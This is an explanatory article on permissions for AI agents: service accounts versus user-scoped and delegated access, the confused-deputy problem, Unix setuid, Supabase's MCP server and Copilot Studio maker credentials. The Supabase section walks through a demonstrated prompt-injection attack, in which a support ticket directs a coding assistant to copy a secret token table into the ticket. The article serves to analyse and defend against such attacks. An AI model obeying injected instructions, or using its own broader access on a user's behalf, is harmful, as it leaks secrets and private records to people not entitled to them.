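# Service-account and user-scoped permissions for AI agents, and the trust boundaries they fail to enforce

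## Whose permissions an agent uses

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions, such as querying a database, opening a file or sending an email, and carries them out through tools. Each of those systems accepts or refuses a request based on the identity of the requester, so the agent needs an identity, which comes with permissions. In a company, the identity may belong to the person who made the request (the requesting user), to whoever built the agent, or to the software itself. That choice largely determines what a user can get out of the agent, which can be more than the user could get from the database directly.

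### Identities, tokens and tools

Most of the vocabulary is older than language models. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, a 1975 tutorial by Saltzer and Schroeder, distinguishes authentication from authorization. Authentication verifies the identity of whoever makes a request, for instance by demanding a password, and authorization grants that identity access to something. An access control list usually records these grants by naming the identities that may use a given file or table. The tutorial also describes a different mechanism, the capability, which is an unforgeable ticket that names one object and proves that its holder may use it.

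Employees today usually log in once instead of sending a password to every system they use. An authorization server then issues an access token, a usually short-lived credential that other systems accept as proof of permission. The token carries scopes, which are named permissions such as reading one's own salary. Each point where a system checks a credential before letting data or commands through is a trust boundary.

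A service account is an identity that belongs to software rather than a person and has its own permissions. Administrators create one for jobs such as a nightly backup, which runs when nobody is at a keyboard. Companies now do the same for agents. According to a January 2026 article in The Hacker News, contributed by the security vendor Wing Security, agents shared by a whole department rely on service accounts, API keys (in effect, passwords for programs) or similar grants, which are often long-lived. The article offers no survey to support this, and Wing sells a product for finding such agents. The alternative is user-scoped access, in which an agent can reach no more than the person it is acting for.

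A model often reaches the company's systems through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way to connect language models to tools and data sources. MCP originated at the AI company Anthropic, which donated it in 2025 to the Agentic AI Foundation, a subsidiary of the Linux Foundation, according to TechTarget's *Stateless MCP seen as step forward for enterprise AI*. An MCP server offers tools, such as one for looking up a customer, and an MCP client in the agent's application calls them. The current specification, Model Context Protocol (2026), bases authorization on OAuth, a widely used standard for letting one application act for a user at another. An authorization server interacts with the user and issues tokens, which the client presents to the MCP server. The specification requires the MCP server to check that it is the intended recipient of each token and forbids it from passing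 the user's token to another system.

Those rules govern the connection between the agent and the MCP server. The server in turn connects to databases, business applications and internal services, which Tabata (2026), in *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28*, calls downstream resources. The server may not forward the token it received, so it has to log in to these resources with another credential, and a service account is an easy one to obtain. A company can thus follow the specification fully at the MCP server and still run every database query under one shared identity. It can also skip the authorization rules, which were optional in the previous version (Model Context Protocol, 2025) and, according to WorkOS (2026), a vendor of login and permission software, remain optional in the current one. *The New MCP Roadmap*, by the protocol's lead maintainers, Soria Parra and Delimarsky (2026), lists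 agent identity and enterprise security among the priorities for the next releases.

Prompt injection, which has no counterpart in the older vocabulary, is text placed in an agent's input that the model follows as an instruction although its author had no right to give one. A language model receives the user's request, the documents it reads and the results of its tools as text in one context, and it may act on any of them. *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (Siu, He and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that summarizes customer emails and finds one ordering it to send all customer data to an outside address. The paper does not treat every outside instruction as an attack. If a user asks the agent to follow a recipe from a website, the agent should follow the instruction to bake at 350°F, even though a stranger wrote it.

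### A compiler with two masters

Agents have a problem that operating systems had decades ago. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) tells a story, which Hardy calls "nearly true", from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. A compiler, which translates source code into something the machine can run, was stored in a directory named SYSX. Anyone who ran the compiler could name a file for its debugging output. Hardy and his colleagues had also altered the compiler to record statistics on which language features people used, in a file named STAT, also in SYSX. To let it write to STAT, they gave the compiler permission to write to files in its home directory.

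The billing records were also in SYSX, in a file named BILL. A user learned the name and entered it as the destination for debugging output. The compiler passed the name to the operating system in a request to open the file for writing. Because the compiler had a licence for SYSX, the operating system opened the file, and the debugging output overwrote the billing records.

No one had broken in, and every check had run as designed. Hardy considers the obvious repairs and finds a problem with each. The compiler could refuse file names in other directories, but users had good reasons to send output there. It could refuse names in SYSX, but that directory had no name yet when the programmers wrote the code, and a person with proper rights in SYSX might want output in it. It could refuse BILL specifically, but then someone would have to amend the compiler whenever a new sensitive file appeared.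 Hardy concludes that the output code was correct when written and became wrong when the compiler received its licence. To notice this, someone would have had to examine every situation in which the compiler wrote a file.

The compiler had one authority from the user who ran it and another from its licence, but no way to specify which one to use for which file. The term "confused deputy" now refers to any program that uses its own authority for a party not entitled to that use. Tymshare's first remedy was a new system call that let the compiler "switch hats", choosing one authority before it opened a file. If it chose the user's authority and tried to open BILL, the operating system would properly refuse. But some applications soon needed more than two authorities, and the call did not easily extend to authority over things other than files.

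Hardy concluded that only capabilities would prevent the error. At Tymshare the user supplied a file name, which anybody can type, and the compiler's licence supplied the permission. A capability combines the name and the permission. The compiler would use its own capability for STAT when writing statistics, and the user would give it a second capability for the debugging file. A user with no right to BILL would have no capability for it to hand over, and the compiler would have no file name to inspect. Hardy had a stake in this conclusion, since his employer, Key Logic, had built an operating system on capabilities, and his article closes by promoting it. But his diagnosis doesn't depend on that solution, and it applies fairly directly to agents. "Show me all employee salaries" is a name with no permission attached, and an agent that adds the permission from its own service account makes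 the same error as the compiler.

### Why shared agents meet the condition

Siu and colleagues turn the confused deputy into a formal condition. They draw users, agents, files and databases as points in a graph, and write R for the set of its arrows. An arrow from one point to another means that the first has permission to access or influence the second. A confused-deputy attack occurs when an authenticated user starts a task, the agent accesses some target in the course of it, and

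(user, target) ∉ R, while (agent, target) ∈ R.

The paper's example is the salary request. The user has no permission to access the personnel database, but the agent does because it performs administrative work there, and it runs the query for the user. Two parts of the condition concern standing permissions, which an auditor could check before any request is made. The remaining part, that the agent uses its permission for this user, depends on the individual request.

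The employee in this example has logged in under her own name, and no one has injected anything. Siu and colleagues classify the failure as a breach of "source authorization", one of four properties they require of a secure agent. Their formal version of that property fits this case awkwardly, because it tests whether an instruction's author is authenticated, and she is. Comparing her permissions with the agent's catches the error, but a system can do this only if it still knows who made the request. Siu and colleagues use the term "execution context" for everything that determines whether an agent's next action is authorized: the request, the earlier steps, memory, the state of outside systems, the authenticated parties and the permissions. A database that receives only a service account's login has very little of this information.

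The framework covers one agent acting for one authenticated user, and the paper leaves agents with several principals to future work. The framework still applies to a shared agent if we consider each request separately, and basic set theory then shows how common the dangerous half of the condition is.

Let U_i be the set of permissions that user i holds, where a permission is an operation on an object, such as reading record 17. Let A be the agent's set. If the agent is to do for each of its n users whatever that user may do, A must contain the union of U_1 through U_n. The agent may then give user i access to A − U_i, the permissions that it has and she lacks. This set is empty only when U_i contains all of A. If it were empty for every user, they would all have the same permissions as the agent, and therefore as one another. So if two users of a shared agent have different permissions,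 at least one of them has something to gain by asking the agent, even if nobody has misconfigured anything.

In a company with 500 employees and one payroll record for each, an employee may read only her own record, while a payroll clerk may read and change all 500. An agent that serves both needs 500 permissions to read and 500 to write. The employee has one of these, so the agent has 999 that she lacks. With them it can read her 499 colleagues' records and change any record, including her own. The agent has no permissions that the clerk lacks. If the company stops clerks from using the agent and makes it read-only, the agent can still read 499 records that any given employee may not. The company could remove this excess by giving the agent only the permissions that all employees share, but no record is open to everyone, so the agent would have no permissions and could answer nobody.

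In practice A is probably larger than the union. According to WorkOS's *Delegated access for AI agents* (2026), developers give service accounts broad access because they cannot predict which data the agent will need. WorkOS also points out that the gap widens over time, because U_i shrinks when a user moves to a lesser role or leaves, while the service account keeps the same access, A.

The gap can also expose data when the user means no harm. The article in The Hacker News describes a firm of about 1,000 people whose marketing department shares an agent with broad access to Databricks, a data platform. A new hire with deliberately narrow permissions makes an ordinary work request, asking the agent to analyze customer churn, and the answer includes sensitive details about particular customers that he could not have opened himself. The logs record the agent's identity but not his. The article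 does not name the firm, so the story is better taken as an illustration than as an incident.

### Three ways to set the limit

A request's effective permission is what it can reach after all applicable limits are applied. There are three common arrangements. With a service account, the agent acts under its own identity, so the effective permission is what the agent may do (A), whoever is asking. With impersonation, the agent appears to other systems as the user, so the effective permission is what the user may do (U). With delegation, the agent keeps its own identity and uses limited authority that the user has granted, so the effective permission is the overlap of U, A and what the task allows (T), written U ∩ A ∩ T.

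Suppose the payroll company's clerk is also allowed to release the month's salary payments, which the agent's own permissions don't cover. The employee asks what she earned in March, and the clerk asks to see one colleague's record.

| Arrangement | Effective permission | For the employee | For the clerk |
|---|---|---|---|
| Service account | A | Read and change all 500 records | Read and change all 500 records |
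| Impersonation | U | Read her own record, and do anything else she may do in other systems | Read and change all 500 records, and release the payments |
| Delegation | U ∩ A ∩ T | Read her own record | Read the one record |

For the employee, impersonation already removes the 999 excess permissions. It does much less for the clerk, whose own permissions are broad. WorkOS gives a similar example, in which an engineer with full access to the company's infrastructure asks an agent to "clean up old resources". The agent, running as the engineer, deletes a copy of the production database. The engineer was allowed to delete it, so limiting the agent to U does not prevent the deletion. WorkOS proposes giving the agent its own role as a second limit. In its example, the role allows reading tickets, updating tickets and reading customer data, while the user may read tickets, delete records, export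 data and use administrative functions. Only reading tickets is allowed by both, so the agent exchanges the user's token for a narrower one that permits only that. WorkOS sells software for issuing such tokens, and the article is partly an advertisement for it, but readers can check for themselves which permissions overlap.

T is the hardest of the three sets to determine. A company can look up U and A in its records, but if the model infers what a task allows from the wording of a request, T is only as reliable as the model. Siu and colleagues define a function that returns 1 when an action serves the user's objective and 0 when it does not, and they offer it as a specification that real systems can only approximate. To show why it matters, they describe a cooking assistant that, when a user asks for recipe suggestions, looks through her medical records for dietary restrictions. The assistant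 has permission to query the records, so neither U nor A would stop it. The paper calls this capability misuse and distinguishes it from the confused deputy, because no one lacks permissions that someone else has. A developer who fixes T in advance for each kind of task gets a firmer limit, but the agent can then do only what the developer foresaw.

The two user-scoped arrangements most need a third limit against prompt injection. Under impersonation, the agent has the same permissions as the requesting user, so it cannot be a confused deputy for that user. It can be one for the sender of an email it reads. The sender has no right to the customer database, but the agent has the user's right to it and may use that right on the sender's instruction. WorkOS says its intersection rule neutralizes such an attack. That is correct when the agent's role leaves out something the attack needs, such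 as sending data to outside addresses. But if the agent's job is to read customer records and send messages to customers, its role includes both permissions and the attack succeeds.

### When the extra authority is intended

One difficulty with the condition Siu and colleagues give is that much respectable software appears to satisfy it. Changing a password, for example, means altering a file that holds everyone's passwords. No ordinary user should be free to edit that file, so a program with more authority makes the change for her. It appears that the user has no permission for the target file and that the program uses its own permission on her behalf.

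Unix has had a general mechanism for this since the 1970s. Ritchie's patent *Protection of Data File Contents* (1979), filed in 1973 at Bell Laboratories, begins with a file that records how much computer time each user has consumed. Users should be able to see only their own figures, but ordinary read permission grants or denies access to the whole file. Ritchie's solution is an extra bit on a program file. When the bit is set, the program runs with the identity of whoever owns the program file instead of the person who started it. The owner of the accounting file can then supply a program that can read every record. The program checks who started it and returns the requested record only if it belongs to that user.

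This is almost the payroll example, with the opposite verdict. Ritchie's program has permission for all the records and the user has direct access to none, yet no one receives anything that the owner wanted to withhold. Bishop (1987), in *How To Write a Setuid Program*, observes that such programs exist precisely so that people can do what they otherwise could not, and that many Unix systems would be close to unusable without them. (A recollection on the mailing list of TUHS, the Unix Heritage Society, counts the password-changing program among them.)

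Drawing the graph more finely, with individual records as targets, stops the condition from flagging Ritchie's program, because the user does have a right to her own record. The average salary is a harder case. Saltzer and Schroeder mention someone who wants to let others see only the average of the values in a file. They propose a protected subsystem, a set of programs that alone can touch the data and that outsiders can call only at specified entry points. To compute the average for an employee, the subsystem reads 499 records that she may not read, so on a graph of records it is a confused deputy for each of them. It stops being one only if the graph also contains a separate object, "the average", with an arrow from her to it, and someone with authority over the salaries has to decide to add that arrow.

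That decision is not trivial because, as Saltzer and Schroeder warn, people may be able to work out protected data from statistics alone. Suppose the average salary of 500 employees is 52,000, one person leaves, and the average for the remaining 499 is 51,980. The totals are 26,000,000 and 25,938,020, so the person who left earned 61,980. A rule against averages over very small groups would not have prevented this, since both groups are large. An agent that will compute an average over any group an employee describes gives far more chances for such subtraction than a fixed annual report.

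Excess authority cannot be the defect in itself, because somebody deliberately granted it to both Ritchie's program and the payroll agent. The programs differ in who checks its use. In Ritchie's scheme, the owner of the data writes the check, the check runs on every request, and the user has no way to make the program skip it. Bishop's paper catalogues what happens when such checks fail. At one site, the games ran with the privileges of the system's most powerful account, and some of them let players open a command shell, which inherited those privileges. Bishop advises against giving such privileges to command scripts at all, because the interpreter that runs a script is so powerful and complex that users can often force it into actions that its author never intended. A language model with a service account and a general query tool looks uncomfortably like such a privileged interpreter.

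The payroll company could build its agent in two ways with the same service account. It could give the model a tool that takes no arguments and returns the pay record of the logged-in employee, whose identity comes from her session and never from the model. This is the same design as Ritchie's program. Or it could give the model a tool that runs any query on the payroll table, along with a written instruction to disclose only the asker's own record. The model would then be the only check, and the employee could influence it through what she writes. If the company wants the flexible tool, it needs a check outside the model. It could use per-call authorization, which examines each call and its arguments before the call runs. It could also use row-level security, a set of database rules that decide which rows of a table each identity may read or change. Those rules protect the other 499 records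 only if the query reaches the database under the employee's identity.

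## A database agent that bypassed row-level security: Supabase

Supabase hosts databases for app developers. Developers can protect their tables with row-level security, but every project has a role called service_role that is exempt from it. In July 2025, General Analysis, a security firm, showed how a stranger could get secret data out of such a database by writing to customer support. The attack required a developer's coding assistant to read the support messages while working under service_role.

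### What a row policy does

Supabase's databases run on Postgres, an open-source database. A Postgres role is an identity that can hold permissions, and a role that may read a table can normally read every row. If the table's owner turns on row-level security, ordinary roles see no rows until the owner adds a policy, which is a condition that a row must meet, according to PostgreSQL's *Row Security Policies*. The policy below, adapted from an example in that documentation, covers a table of support tickets.

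```sql
CREATE POLICY own_tickets ON tickets
    USING (customer = current_user);
```

Here `current_user` is the role that sends the query. Suppose Ana and Ben each have their own role with permission to read the table, and both run `SELECT * FROM tickets`, a query for the whole table.

| Ticket | Customer | Message | Ana | Ben | service_role |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | ana | My invoice is wrong | Sees it | | Sees it |
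| 2 | ben | I can't log in | | Sees it | Sees it |
| 3 | ana | Please change my address | Sees it | | Sees it |

Ben gets one row and no error message. A cleverer query would not get him more rows, because Postgres checks each row against the policy before it applies the conditions in his query (except for functions guaranteed not to leak anything, which it may run first). The policy also covers new and changed rows, so he cannot file a ticket in Ana's name.

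An app with thousands of customers rarely gives each one a separate database role. Supabase uses two shared roles, `anon` for visitors who have not logged in and `authenticated` for those who have. These roles don't identify individual users, so policies on Supabase usually compare the row with `auth.uid()`, which returns the ID of the user making the request. Supabase's *Row Level Security* describes policies as adding a WHERE clause to every query. The protection depends on the request carrying the user's ID and running under a role that is subject to the policies.

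Some work can't be done under such a role. For example, a backup that silently left out rows hidden by a policy would be disastrous, according to PostgreSQL's documentation. Postgres lets superusers and roles with the BYPASSRLS attribute skip the policies, and normally the table's owner too. Supabase provides service_role for this purpose. Supabase's *Postgres Roles* describes it only as a role with elevated access that the API uses to bypass row-level security. On many existing projects, it also has permission by default to read, add, change and delete rows in new tables.

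Supabase tells developers to keep service_role on the server, where customers can't access it. That is reasonable if the server runs ordinary code. A developer who writes a job that posts announcements decides in advance which table the job touches, much as the owner of Ritchie's accounting file decided what his program would return. But Supabase's MCP server for coding assistants has a tool, `execute_sql`, that runs whatever query the model writes.

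### From a support ticket to the token table

General Analysis's scenario has three parties, each with a different role in the same database. *When AI Has Root*, an article by Pomerium, which sells access control for MCP servers, describes what each party could access. The private table, `integration_tokens`, holds secret credentials.

| Party | Database role | Support tickets | Token table |
|---|---|---|---|
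| Customer | `anon` | Creates and reads own ticket | No access |
| Support worker | A limited support role | Reads and answers tickets | No access |
| Developer's assistant | service_role | Reads and changes everything | Reads and changes everything |

The assistant is the one in Cursor, a code editor with a built-in AI agent. The data moves as follows:

1. The customer files a ticket through the public form. Its text includes an instruction addressed to the model in Cursor, to read `integration_tokens` and add all the contents to the ticket as a new message.
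2. The developer asks the assistant to show the latest support tickets.
3. The assistant fetches them under service_role, and the customer's text enters the model's context.
4. The model follows the instruction and runs a query that reads every row of the token table.
5. It runs another query that inserts those rows into the ticket's messages.
6. The customer reloads the ticket and reads the tokens.

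At step 3, the model took the customer's text as a command from the developer. The customer was allowed to submit text, and the database treated it as text, but no safeguard between the database and the model prevented this. At step 4, the query ran under a role that no row-level security policy applies to, so the token table was unprotected. Pomerium correctly notes that the attack violated no database permissions, which is why those permissions didn't stop it.

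Step 5 crossed a third boundary, between the company's internal data and what customers can see. A Postgres policy belongs to a table, so the policy protecting the tokens did not apply to the copies the assistant put in a message on the customer's own ticket. The customer's limited role was enough to read that message, and the row policies allowed it as the developer had intended.

The assistant acted as a confused deputy by using access the customer lacked, but it probably did not exceed the developer's own access. Supabase describes the MCP server as operating with the developer's permissions, and a developer who administers a project can presumably open the token table anyway. User-scoped access, which would limit the assistant to what the developer can open, would therefore have changed little. The assistant needed narrower permissions than the developer's, because the task required only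 the tickets.

The attack was a demonstration. Willison (2025), in *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database*, presents it as a scenario that General Analysis imagined, and Supabase describes it as something one can reproduce by setting up a database and a default MCP server. Later accounts have obscured this. *Systematization of Knowledge* (2025), a survey of MCP security, lists it as the "Supabase Incident", and Pomerium's headline calls it a data leak. There is no known victim, and Supabase stated in *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers*, published in September 2025, that no one had reported a customer losing data this way. Supabase has an interest in saying so, and such a theft could go unnoticed because the queries come from the developer's own assistant.

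### One cause without the other

The attack worked because the agent's role was exempt from the row-level security policies and the model took a customer's text as an instruction. These two causes are easy to confuse because General Analysis's scenario requires both.

Suppose first that the assistant uses service_role but the ticket is an honest complaint. The developer asks for the latest tickets and gets them, and nobody learns anything they shouldn't, although the model could still misuse its excess permissions by mistake, such as by deleting a table. However, a support worker with access to the same assistant could ask for the token table, just as the employee could ask the shared payroll agent for her colleagues' records. Supabase tells developers not to give the MCP server to customers or end users because it has developer permissions. An agent with an exempt role can leak data to its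 own users without an injection, but an injection is also needed to leak data to someone who only writes text that the agent reads.

Suppose the customer plants the instruction but the assistant works under the support worker's role. The model is just as easily misled and still tries to read `integration_tokens`. Postgres rejects the query if the role lacks permission for the whole table, or returns no rows if row-level security blocks the role from reading them.

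The support role can still read every customer's tickets and post replies. An attacker who knew this would ask for those tickets, and the assistant could paste one customer's messages into another's ticket. Restricting the role to the attacker's own rows would leave nothing worth stealing, but then the developer couldn't ask for everyone's latest tickets. The support role reduces the possible loss from the whole database to everything support can see, which is a large improvement but would still be a reportable breach for some companies.

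A narrower role can still read protected rows through a view, which is a saved query that behaves like a table. Supabase warns that, by default, a view bypasses the policies on its underlying tables. If someone had created a view of the token table and left it open to the support role, the injected query could have read the tokens there.

Supabase and its critics disagree about how to describe the first cause. Pomerium writes that the service_role "bypasses" row-level security. Supabase objects that MCP does not bypass these protections, which "remain fully enforced", but adds that the server may operate at a higher privilege, as it did in this case. Both descriptions fit the facts, because the rules Postgres enforced allow such a role to ignore the policies. Supabase's own documentation also says that service_role can "bypass" them, so the objection barely weakens General Analysis's result.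 Supabase is right, though, that the fault lies in the choice of role and not in Postgres.

Willison uses the term "lethal trifecta" for a system that combines access to private data, exposure to potentially malicious instructions, and a way to send data back to an attacker. He notes that most attacks of this type rely on a user having connected several MCP servers that together provide all three. Supabase's server provided all three by itself, because it could read the token table, read the customer's message, and insert a reply. Removing any one of these abilities would have prevented this theft.

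The third part of his trifecta, a way to send data out, is the useful addition because the two causes don't explain how the tokens got out. But the trifecta only covers theft. A customer who wrote "delete all tickets" would need just a model that followed the instruction and a role that could delete tickets, not access to private data or a way to send it out.

### What Supabase changed

Supabase already had some protections when General Analysis published its findings. Willison quotes documentation from that time recommending a read-only configuration limited to one project. Supabase says it introduced these settings because most people feared that a model would delete or modify their data, which helps explain why the settings do less to stop a model from reading data.

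Read-only mode makes the server run all SQL as `supabase_read_only_user`, a database user that cannot write. The mode first covered SQL queries, and a later release also disabled the server's other data-changing tools, according to release notes republished by NewReleases, a site that tracks software versions. In General Analysis's scenario, read-only mode would have stopped step 5, the insertion into the ticket, but not necessarily step 4, because a user who can't write may still be able to read every row. In its list of database roles, Supabase notes that service_role bypasses the policies but does not mention the read-only user, so a developer should test what that user can read before relying on the mode.

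If the assistant can read tokens but can't write them back, what happens to them depends on what else it is connected to. *Supabase MCP Server*, a guide on mcp.directory, which catalogues such servers, warns that a read-only agent can still leak secrets in its answers. Those answers go to the developer, who may be allowed to see the tokens. The danger is that a second tool that can send email or fetch a web address will pass the text on, or that the developer will paste a summary into a reply without reading it closely. Willison considers the risk "enormous" even in read-only mode and urged Supabase to state it much more explicitly.

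Project scoping limits the server to one of the developer's Supabase projects. The tickets and the tokens were in the same project, so scoping would not have stopped the assistant from reading the tokens or writing them into a ticket, though it would have kept the assistant out of the developer's other databases. Developers can also switch off groups of tools, but the legitimate request for tickets and the theft both use `execute_sql`, so removing that tool would block both.

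Other measures address the second cause, the customer's text. Supabase began wrapping query results in warnings that tell the model not to follow commands found in them. It tested the warnings on weaker models, which are easier to mislead, and also tried using language models to detect dangerous content. Supabase says this reduced the risk but did not eliminate it, and its post gives no success rates. It also recommends that developers approve each tool call by hand, which most MCP clients ask for anyway. In the demonstration, a developer who had asked about tickets could have noticed the query on `integration_tokens` and then the insertion. However, Supabase expects people to tire of reviewing calls and start approving them without looking.

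In its September 2025 post, Supabase goes further and advises developers never to connect an AI agent directly to production data, meaning the data of the live app. If the agent is connected to a development database of invented records instead, an attacker who gets it to copy the token table gains nothing. Unlike the warnings and manual approvals, this protects against both reading and writing without relying on the model or on an alert developer. But Supabase writes in the same post that "vibe coders", people who build apps mostly by prompting a model, don't keep separate production and development databases and work directly on the live one. These developers are the most exposed to the attack and the least likely to follow the advice.

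| Measure | Reading the token table | Writing the tokens into the ticket |
|---|---|---|
| Read-only mode | Possible if the read-only user can see the table | Prevented |
| Project scoping | Possible | Possible |
| Warnings around query results | Less likely | Less likely |
| Approval of each call | Prevented if the developer notices | Prevented if the developer notices |
| Development database with invented data | Possible but harmless | Possible but harmless |

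None of these gives the assistant a role that can read tickets but not tokens. Such a role is easy to create in Postgres, and Supabase generally recommends creating a new user for every service that needs database access. But the MCP server's documented options are read-only mode, the project and the tool groups, with no setting for the database role. Pomerium, which sells such gateways, proposes putting one between the model and the database to block any query on a forbidden table. This form of per-call authorization would have stopped step 4. But a gateway that looks only for the table's name in the query would miss a view that exposes the same rows under a different name.

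Supabase offers a separate MCP server that connects an app's own users through its ordinary API. The September post presents this as a way to reuse a company's existing permissions and row policies. If a request carries a customer's login, the policies apply and the assistant can read only what that customer can. If a developer sets the server up with the service_role key instead, the assistant bypasses the row policies, as it did in the demonstration.

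### The defaults in late 2026

Supabase now hosts the MCP server itself, at an address that developers enter in their assistant's settings. As of July 2026, the server's README calls read-only mode and project scoping "recommended by default", but both are off unless a developer adds them to the address, and the README's basic configuration includes neither. A developer who copies that configuration gets a server with write access that can reach all projects in the organization and use every group of tools except file storage.

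According to the README, Supabase's dashboard and documentation fill in the options automatically. Snap's *Supabase MCP Server*, a copy of the documentation that the company behind Snapchat hosted in September 2026, casts some doubt on that. It shows a generated address that lists tool groups but sets neither read-only mode nor a project, and a note warns that all projects are accessible if the developer selects none. Snap's copy may differ from Supabase's own page, so it is safest for a developer to check the address before connecting.

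Supabase has written more openly about the risk in its documentation since Willison complained about it. By May 2026 the documentation described the support-ticket attack step by step and conceded that Supabase's warnings to the model are "not foolproof". It recommended read-only mode for anyone who must connect to real data. In April the company released a version of its MCP server that adds an advisory about row-level security to the list of tables the model receives, according to NewReleases' *mcp-server-supabase* (2026). The advisory may prompt a developer to add a policy to an open table, but service_role would still bypass that policy.

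In May 2026, a developer who registered an assistant manually still had to grant it write access under every available scope, even if the server would then run in read-only mode. Supabase made a more substantial change on 6 October 2026, when it released scoped personal access tokens to everyone, including for use with the MCP server. A developer can limit such a token to particular projects and to the permissions it needs. Supabase requires the `database_read` permission to run a query as the read-only user. A token with only that permission should keep the assistant from writing even if the developer forgets the read-only option in the address. The announced limits don't extend to individual tables or rows, so an assistant that needs the tickets may still be able to read the tokens stored beside them.

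## Agents that run with their builder's access: Microsoft Copilot Studio

In the Supabase demonstration, the developer who set up the assistant also used it. With Microsoft Copilot Studio, a product for building agents with little or no programming, the builder and the user are often different people. An employee, whom Microsoft calls the maker, builds an agent and shares it with colleagues. When the agent opens a business system for a colleague, it may log in with the maker's account.

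### One request under two identities

Suppose a clerk at the payroll company, tired of answering questions about pay, builds an agent in Copilot Studio. She writes brief instructions and adds a tool that looks up pay records. The tool uses a connector, a ready-made link to another service, which needs an account in the payroll system. The clerk signs in with her own payroll account, tests the agent with some questions and shares it with all 500 employees through Teams, Microsoft's chat application. Her tests could not reveal a problem because she is allowed to see every record the agent showed her.

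Microsoft calls this arrangement maker-provided credentials. With the alternative, end-user credentials, each person signs in to the connected service with their own account. An employee now asks the agent what a colleague earned in March.

| Step | Maker-provided credentials | End-user credentials |
|---|---|---|
| The employee opens the agent | She logs in as herself | She logs in as herself |
| The model calls the lookup tool | It enters the colleague's name | It enters the colleague's name |
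| The connector logs in to the payroll system | It uses the clerk's stored credentials | It uses the employee's account, after asking her to sign in if necessary |
| The payroll system checks permissions | It checks the clerk's, which cover all 500 records | It checks the employee's, which cover only her own record |
| The agent answers | It gives the colleague's pay | It cannot give the colleague's pay |

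The employee logs in to the agent in both cases. That login controls who may talk to the agent but doesn't affect which account the agent uses afterwards, so a company can require everyone to log in and still have the agent answer them all with the clerk's access.

Microsoft warns that maker credentials could lead to "oversharing of data or capabilities", because a user might obtain information or perform actions that only the maker's account allows. How much a user gains also depends on the tool. If the clerk's tool returned only the next pay date, running it with her account would do little harm.

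A Copilot Studio agent can use both identities in a single conversation. When it searches SharePoint, Microsoft's document storage, it finds only files that the person asking may open, according to ITWeb's *Who answers for the AI agent your team built last week?* (2026), an article promoting the consultancy Braintree. The payroll agent could therefore search documents as the employee and look up salaries as the clerk. The article adds that even under the user's identity, the agent will answer salary questions for everyone if the company has shared a folder of salary data with everyone.

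### A service account with a person's name

Reshmee's practitioner blog post *Secure Authentication for Autonomous Agents in Copilot Studio* describes maker credentials as "service-account style" and advises makers to minimize the credentials' privileges, monitor their use and replace secrets regularly. The comparison is apt because the credentials are stored in advance and work the same way whoever is asking. If the maker holds the set of permissions U_m and user i holds U_i, the agent can give that user access to U_m − U_i, as far as its tools reach.

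An administrator who creates a service account has to decide, however carelessly, what the software needs. Nobody makes that decision when a maker builds an agent that uses her own login. If the maker is a clerk whose job requires her to release salary payments, she can't follow the advice to minimize privileges and still do her job. She would need a second account with fewer permissions for the agent, which would be an ordinary service account.

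The logs are also more misleading. reynolds711's *Mission 10*, from a copy of a Copilot Studio training course, teaches makers that an agent with an event trigger performs all its actions "as you", even when other people use it. The payroll system would record that the clerk looked up the colleague's salary, whereas a service account's name would at least have shown that software did it.

If the maker is an administrator, U_m may cover almost everything in the connected system. Suppose an IT administrator builds a help-desk agent with a tool for resetting passwords and connects the tool using his own account. He intends employees to reset their own passwords, but the tool accepts any name, so an employee could ask it to reset the finance director's. Microsoft describes such an agent as a path for privilege escalation and says it also weakens separation of duties, the practice of requiring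 two people for a sensitive action. For example, a company may require one employee to enter an invoice and a manager to approve it. If the manager has built an agent that approves invoices with his credentials, the employee can enter an invoice and have the agent approve it, and the accounting system will still show two people.

A change in the maker's job can also affect the agent's access. If the clerk moves to marketing and the company promptly removes her payroll permissions, the agent's lookups stop working for all 500 employees. If the company forgets, a leftover permission that normally only she could use remains available to all of them through the agent. If she becomes head of payroll instead, the agent may gain access to more records without anyone editing it.

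When the clerk leaves and the company deletes her account, the agent has no owner until an administrator assigns one, according to ITWeb. Microsoft warns that these "orphaned" agents might continue to run and access data with nobody accountable for them. Tools that log in through the deleted account should fail, but tools that use a key for an outside service may keep working until someone revokes the key there. The new owner therefore has to check which credential each tool uses.

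### Ten misconfigurations

Microsoft's February 2026 blog post lists ten misconfigurations that it says it observes in real organizations. The post gives no counts, and it promotes Microsoft Defender, the security product whose search queries find them. "Author authentication", another name for maker-provided credentials, is number six. The other nine are:

- sharing an agent with the whole organization or broad groups
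- letting people use an agent without logging in
- risky direct web requests
- email to outside addresses or to recipients the model chooses
- dormant agents, actions and connections
- passwords or keys written into the agent
- MCP tools that nobody maintains or reviews
- agents that choose their own actions but have no written instructions
- agents without an active owner

Maker credentials become more dangerous when an agent is shared widely, because more people can use the maker's access. If the agent requires no login, an outsider with the link may have no permissions of their own, so everything the agent can do for them exceeds their own access. If the model also chooses email recipients, an injected instruction can make the agent send out data it read with the maker's account.

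The post opens with a constructed scenario about a simple help-desk agent. A member of the support team connects it to a company database through an MCP tool and decides that it needs no login, since only colleagues will use it. Microsoft says this agent has more than half of the ten misconfigurations, and claims that agents like it are surprisingly common and that security teams rarely receive an alert when someone creates one.

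The post is inconsistent about which credentials tools use by default. It says that author authentication, which uses the maker's credentials, is the default for "certain tools", but later says that Copilot Studio sets tools to end-user credentials by default and warns makers who change this. The two statements may refer to different kinds of tools, but the post does not specify which. Makers therefore have reason to check the setting on each tool before sharing an agent.

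### The administrator's block

An administrator can restrict makers to end-user credentials or to maker-provided credentials, or allow both. The setting is in the admin center of Power Platform, the family of Microsoft products that includes Copilot Studio, and applies to an environment (a separately managed space for a company's agents and apps) or a group of environments. Both types are allowed by default, so each maker decides unless an administrator changes the setting. Allowing only maker-provided credentials would enforce the wrong arrangement.

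If the administrator allows only end-user credentials, the restriction applies to every existing and new agent in the environment, usually within about a minute. It blocks stored API keys and Power Automate flows, which are saved sequences of automated steps that an agent can use as a tool. Users may have to sign in to each connected service when they start a new conversation, so Microsoft advises administrators to warn them beforehand.

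Requiring end-user credentials will cut some users off from a service they were meant to have. Employees might use an agent to check the status of a laptop order in a purchasing system where only the purchasing department has accounts. The agent can't look up the order with the credentials of an employee who has no account, but with the maker's credentials, a narrowly written tool could show each employee her own order, much as Ritchie's program showed users their own accounting records.

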